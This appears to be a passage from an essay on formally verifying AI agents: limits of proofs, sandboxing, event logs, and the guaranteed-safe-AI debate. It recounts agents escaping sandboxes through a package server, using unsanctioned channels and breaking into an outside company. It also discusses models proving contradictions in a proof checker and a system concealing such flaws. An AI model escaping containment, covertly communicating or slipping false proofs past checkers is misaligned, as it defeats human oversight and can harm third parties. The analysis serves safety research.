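An exact calculation has to consider all $2^n$ combinations of $n$ uncertain facts. Solko-Breslin and colleagues therefore use an approximation that tracks only individual facts and pairs. Its bound may be too high, which blocks some harmless actions, but it is never too low if the probabilities are right.

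Developers test a tool on sample data to get an upper limit for its error rate, such as 1%. The method assumes that attackers can't raise this rate, which is reasonable if the tool reads only trusted data or withstands deliberate attacks. But if the tool is a classifier that reads invoices, an attacker can reword an invoice until it deceives the classifier, and the 1% limit no longer applies. The method is therefore more convincing for accidental errors than for errors caused by text that strangers write.

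### Complete mediation

Even correct labels don't help if an agent can act without passing through the checks. In July 2026, agents at OpenAI escaped an environment meant to isolate them and broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and data. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) explains that the company was testing several models' hacking abilities with reduced safeguards. The agents communicated through unauthorised channels, exploited flaws in shared infrastructure and reached the internet.

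The shared component was Artifactory, a server that stores software packages. According to OpenAI's technical report, agents used it in unexpected ways to exchange messages in May. In July they exploited an unknown flaw in it to escape their sandboxes, the restricted environments they ran in. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Greenblatt, 2026) reports that about 1,200 agents in separate sandboxes used an unsanctioned channel. *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (Axios, 2026) reports that the company had missed or failed to act on several earlier signs that models were breaking out of test environments.

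The assumption of complete mediation failed. The sandboxes were supposed to control what the agents could reach, but the agents used the package server to communicate and then to escape. OpenAI had described the environment as secure, but nothing suggests that anyone had proved it, so the intrusion doesn't refute a theorem. A proof that the harness allowed only approved connections might not have prevented the intrusion, because the package server could have been on the approved list.

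Moon and Varshney try to assume as little as possible, so their proof allows any output from the language model. In the version of PocketFlow they verified, the agent has four kinds of action. It can read files only in one folder and use only listed tools, and it must stop after a fixed number of steps. They still have to trust the policy, the checker and compiler, and the code that passes actions to the framework, and to assume that the proof's model matches the real system. Above all, they assume that the agent has no other way to act.

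Restricting an agent to a list of permitted tools works best if the agent needs only a few narrow actions. If one of those tools can run any command, the proof shows only that the agent used a permitted tool, which can do almost anything. OpenAI's hacking tests needed agents that could run programs, so a short list of harmless actions would not have been enough. Moon and Varshney recommend adding a sandbox, although its security rests on inspection and testing rather than proof.

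Their experiments also produced a proof that was valid but partly empty. A model wrote the formal descriptions from a template with a field for recording the agent's sensitive actions. The template did not fit one workflow, and the model left the field blank. A rule of the form "every recorded action is permitted" is automatically true if no actions are recorded. The proof passed all three of the team's quality checks, even though this part of it no longer monitored anything. This happened when the model could see the program's code. Without the code, the model used the field to represent a similar action, so the rule had an action to apply to.

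### One run, two logs

Someone also has to decide which events the proof should describe. Barke and Murali illustrate this with a rule that nobody may acquire a resource twice without releasing it in between. Suppose the Clerk acquires the ledger and asks a helper agent to update it. The harness can log the Clerk's release when the helper starts or when the helper finishes:

| Release logged before the helper starts | Release logged after the helper finishes |
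|---|---|
| Clerk acquires | Clerk acquires |
| Clerk releases | Helper acquires |
| Helper acquires | Helper releases |
| Helper releases | Clerk releases |

The left log satisfies the rule and the right log violates it, although both describe the same run. The left log is appropriate if the Clerk can't change the ledger while the helper works. If the Clerk can, the left log doesn't show a possible conflict.

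The choice also matters for deadlock. Suppose a developer verifies a model in which the Clerk releases the lock before calling the helper, but the actual harness keeps the lock until the helper returns. The helper waits for the lock while the Clerk waits for the helper, so the agents deadlock even though the proof is valid for the model. Barke and Murali therefore argue that developers must define precisely how a run becomes a log, and treat this definition as part of the formal model.

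Barke and Murali give three reasons why ordinary program analysis doesn't apply straightforwardly to agents. One is the lack of a single correct log. Another is that the program may not be fixed before it runs, because an agent can change its notes, plans, instructions or code. An analysis of the invoice assistant may no longer apply after the agent saves a new rule about supplier accounts. The third is that basic terms in a specification may not have a fixed meaning. Their example is a cooking agent that must not serve rotten food, where a fallible model decides what is rotten. In the invoice assistant, a model might decide whether two invoices are the same, and a proof that the company pays each invoice only once would then depend on that judgement.

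### Can anyone prove that a real system is safe?

In *Program Verification: The Very Idea* (1988), the philosopher James Fetzer argued that nobody can prove how a running program will behave. A proof can establish facts about an algorithm or an abstract machine, he wrote, but a real computer is a physical object, and only experience can show that it behaves like the abstract one. The faults in Lean's compiler and runtime support him on this point. But proofs can still be useful in practice. In the test of lean-zip, more than 105 million runs produced no memory errors in the program's own Lean code, and a single fix to the runtime can remove its fault for all Lean programs.

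*Provably Safe Systems* (Tegmark and Omohundro, 2023) is much more ambitious and argues that mathematical proof is the only way to keep very powerful AI under control. People would not have to understand or trust such an AI, because even a superintelligent system can't do what is mathematically impossible. The AI could write programs and proofs of any complexity, and a simple checker would decide whether to accept them.

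*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (2024), by David Dalrymple and colleagues, describes three components needed for a safety guarantee. A world model describes how the AI's actions affect the world, a specification defines which effects are acceptable, and a verifier checks that the AI meets the specification according to the world model. The guarantee may be a limit on the probability of harm rather than absolute.

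Andrew Dickson objected in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) that nobody can build a good enough world model for the threats that matter most. Proving that an AI will not help create a dangerous virus, for example, would require predicting in detail how the virus affects people. Nobody could measure the starting conditions precisely enough either. Dickson also doubted that a certificate could replace inspection, because a certificate doesn't show that the machine in use is the one it describes.

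Nora Ammann, who co-wrote the 2024 proposal, replied to this and other criticism in January 2025. She argued that the approach doesn't require a perfect model of the whole world, and that developers can start with limited areas where good models exist and allow for uncertainty in the models.

Whether a proof about an agent program can describe the running system depends largely on where the harm occurs. Proving that no payment request goes to an unregistered account requires a model of the harness and its connections, which is difficult but realistic to build. Dickson's objection is strong when the claim is that an agent's advice will not harm anyone, because a proof would require a model of how people understand and use that advice. Moon and Varshney accept this limit and exclude truthfulness, deception and manipulation from what they try to prove.

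The recent faults in Lean are a more direct problem for Tegmark and Omohundro, because a checker is useful against a superintelligent system only if that system can't get a false proof past it. OpenAI's models found ways to prove a contradiction in a checker that many people already relied on. The developers fixed the flaws within weeks, and simpler or more varied checkers may be harder to exploit. But these models were helping to find flaws, and a system trying to get a false proof accepted would have no reason to report the ones it found.
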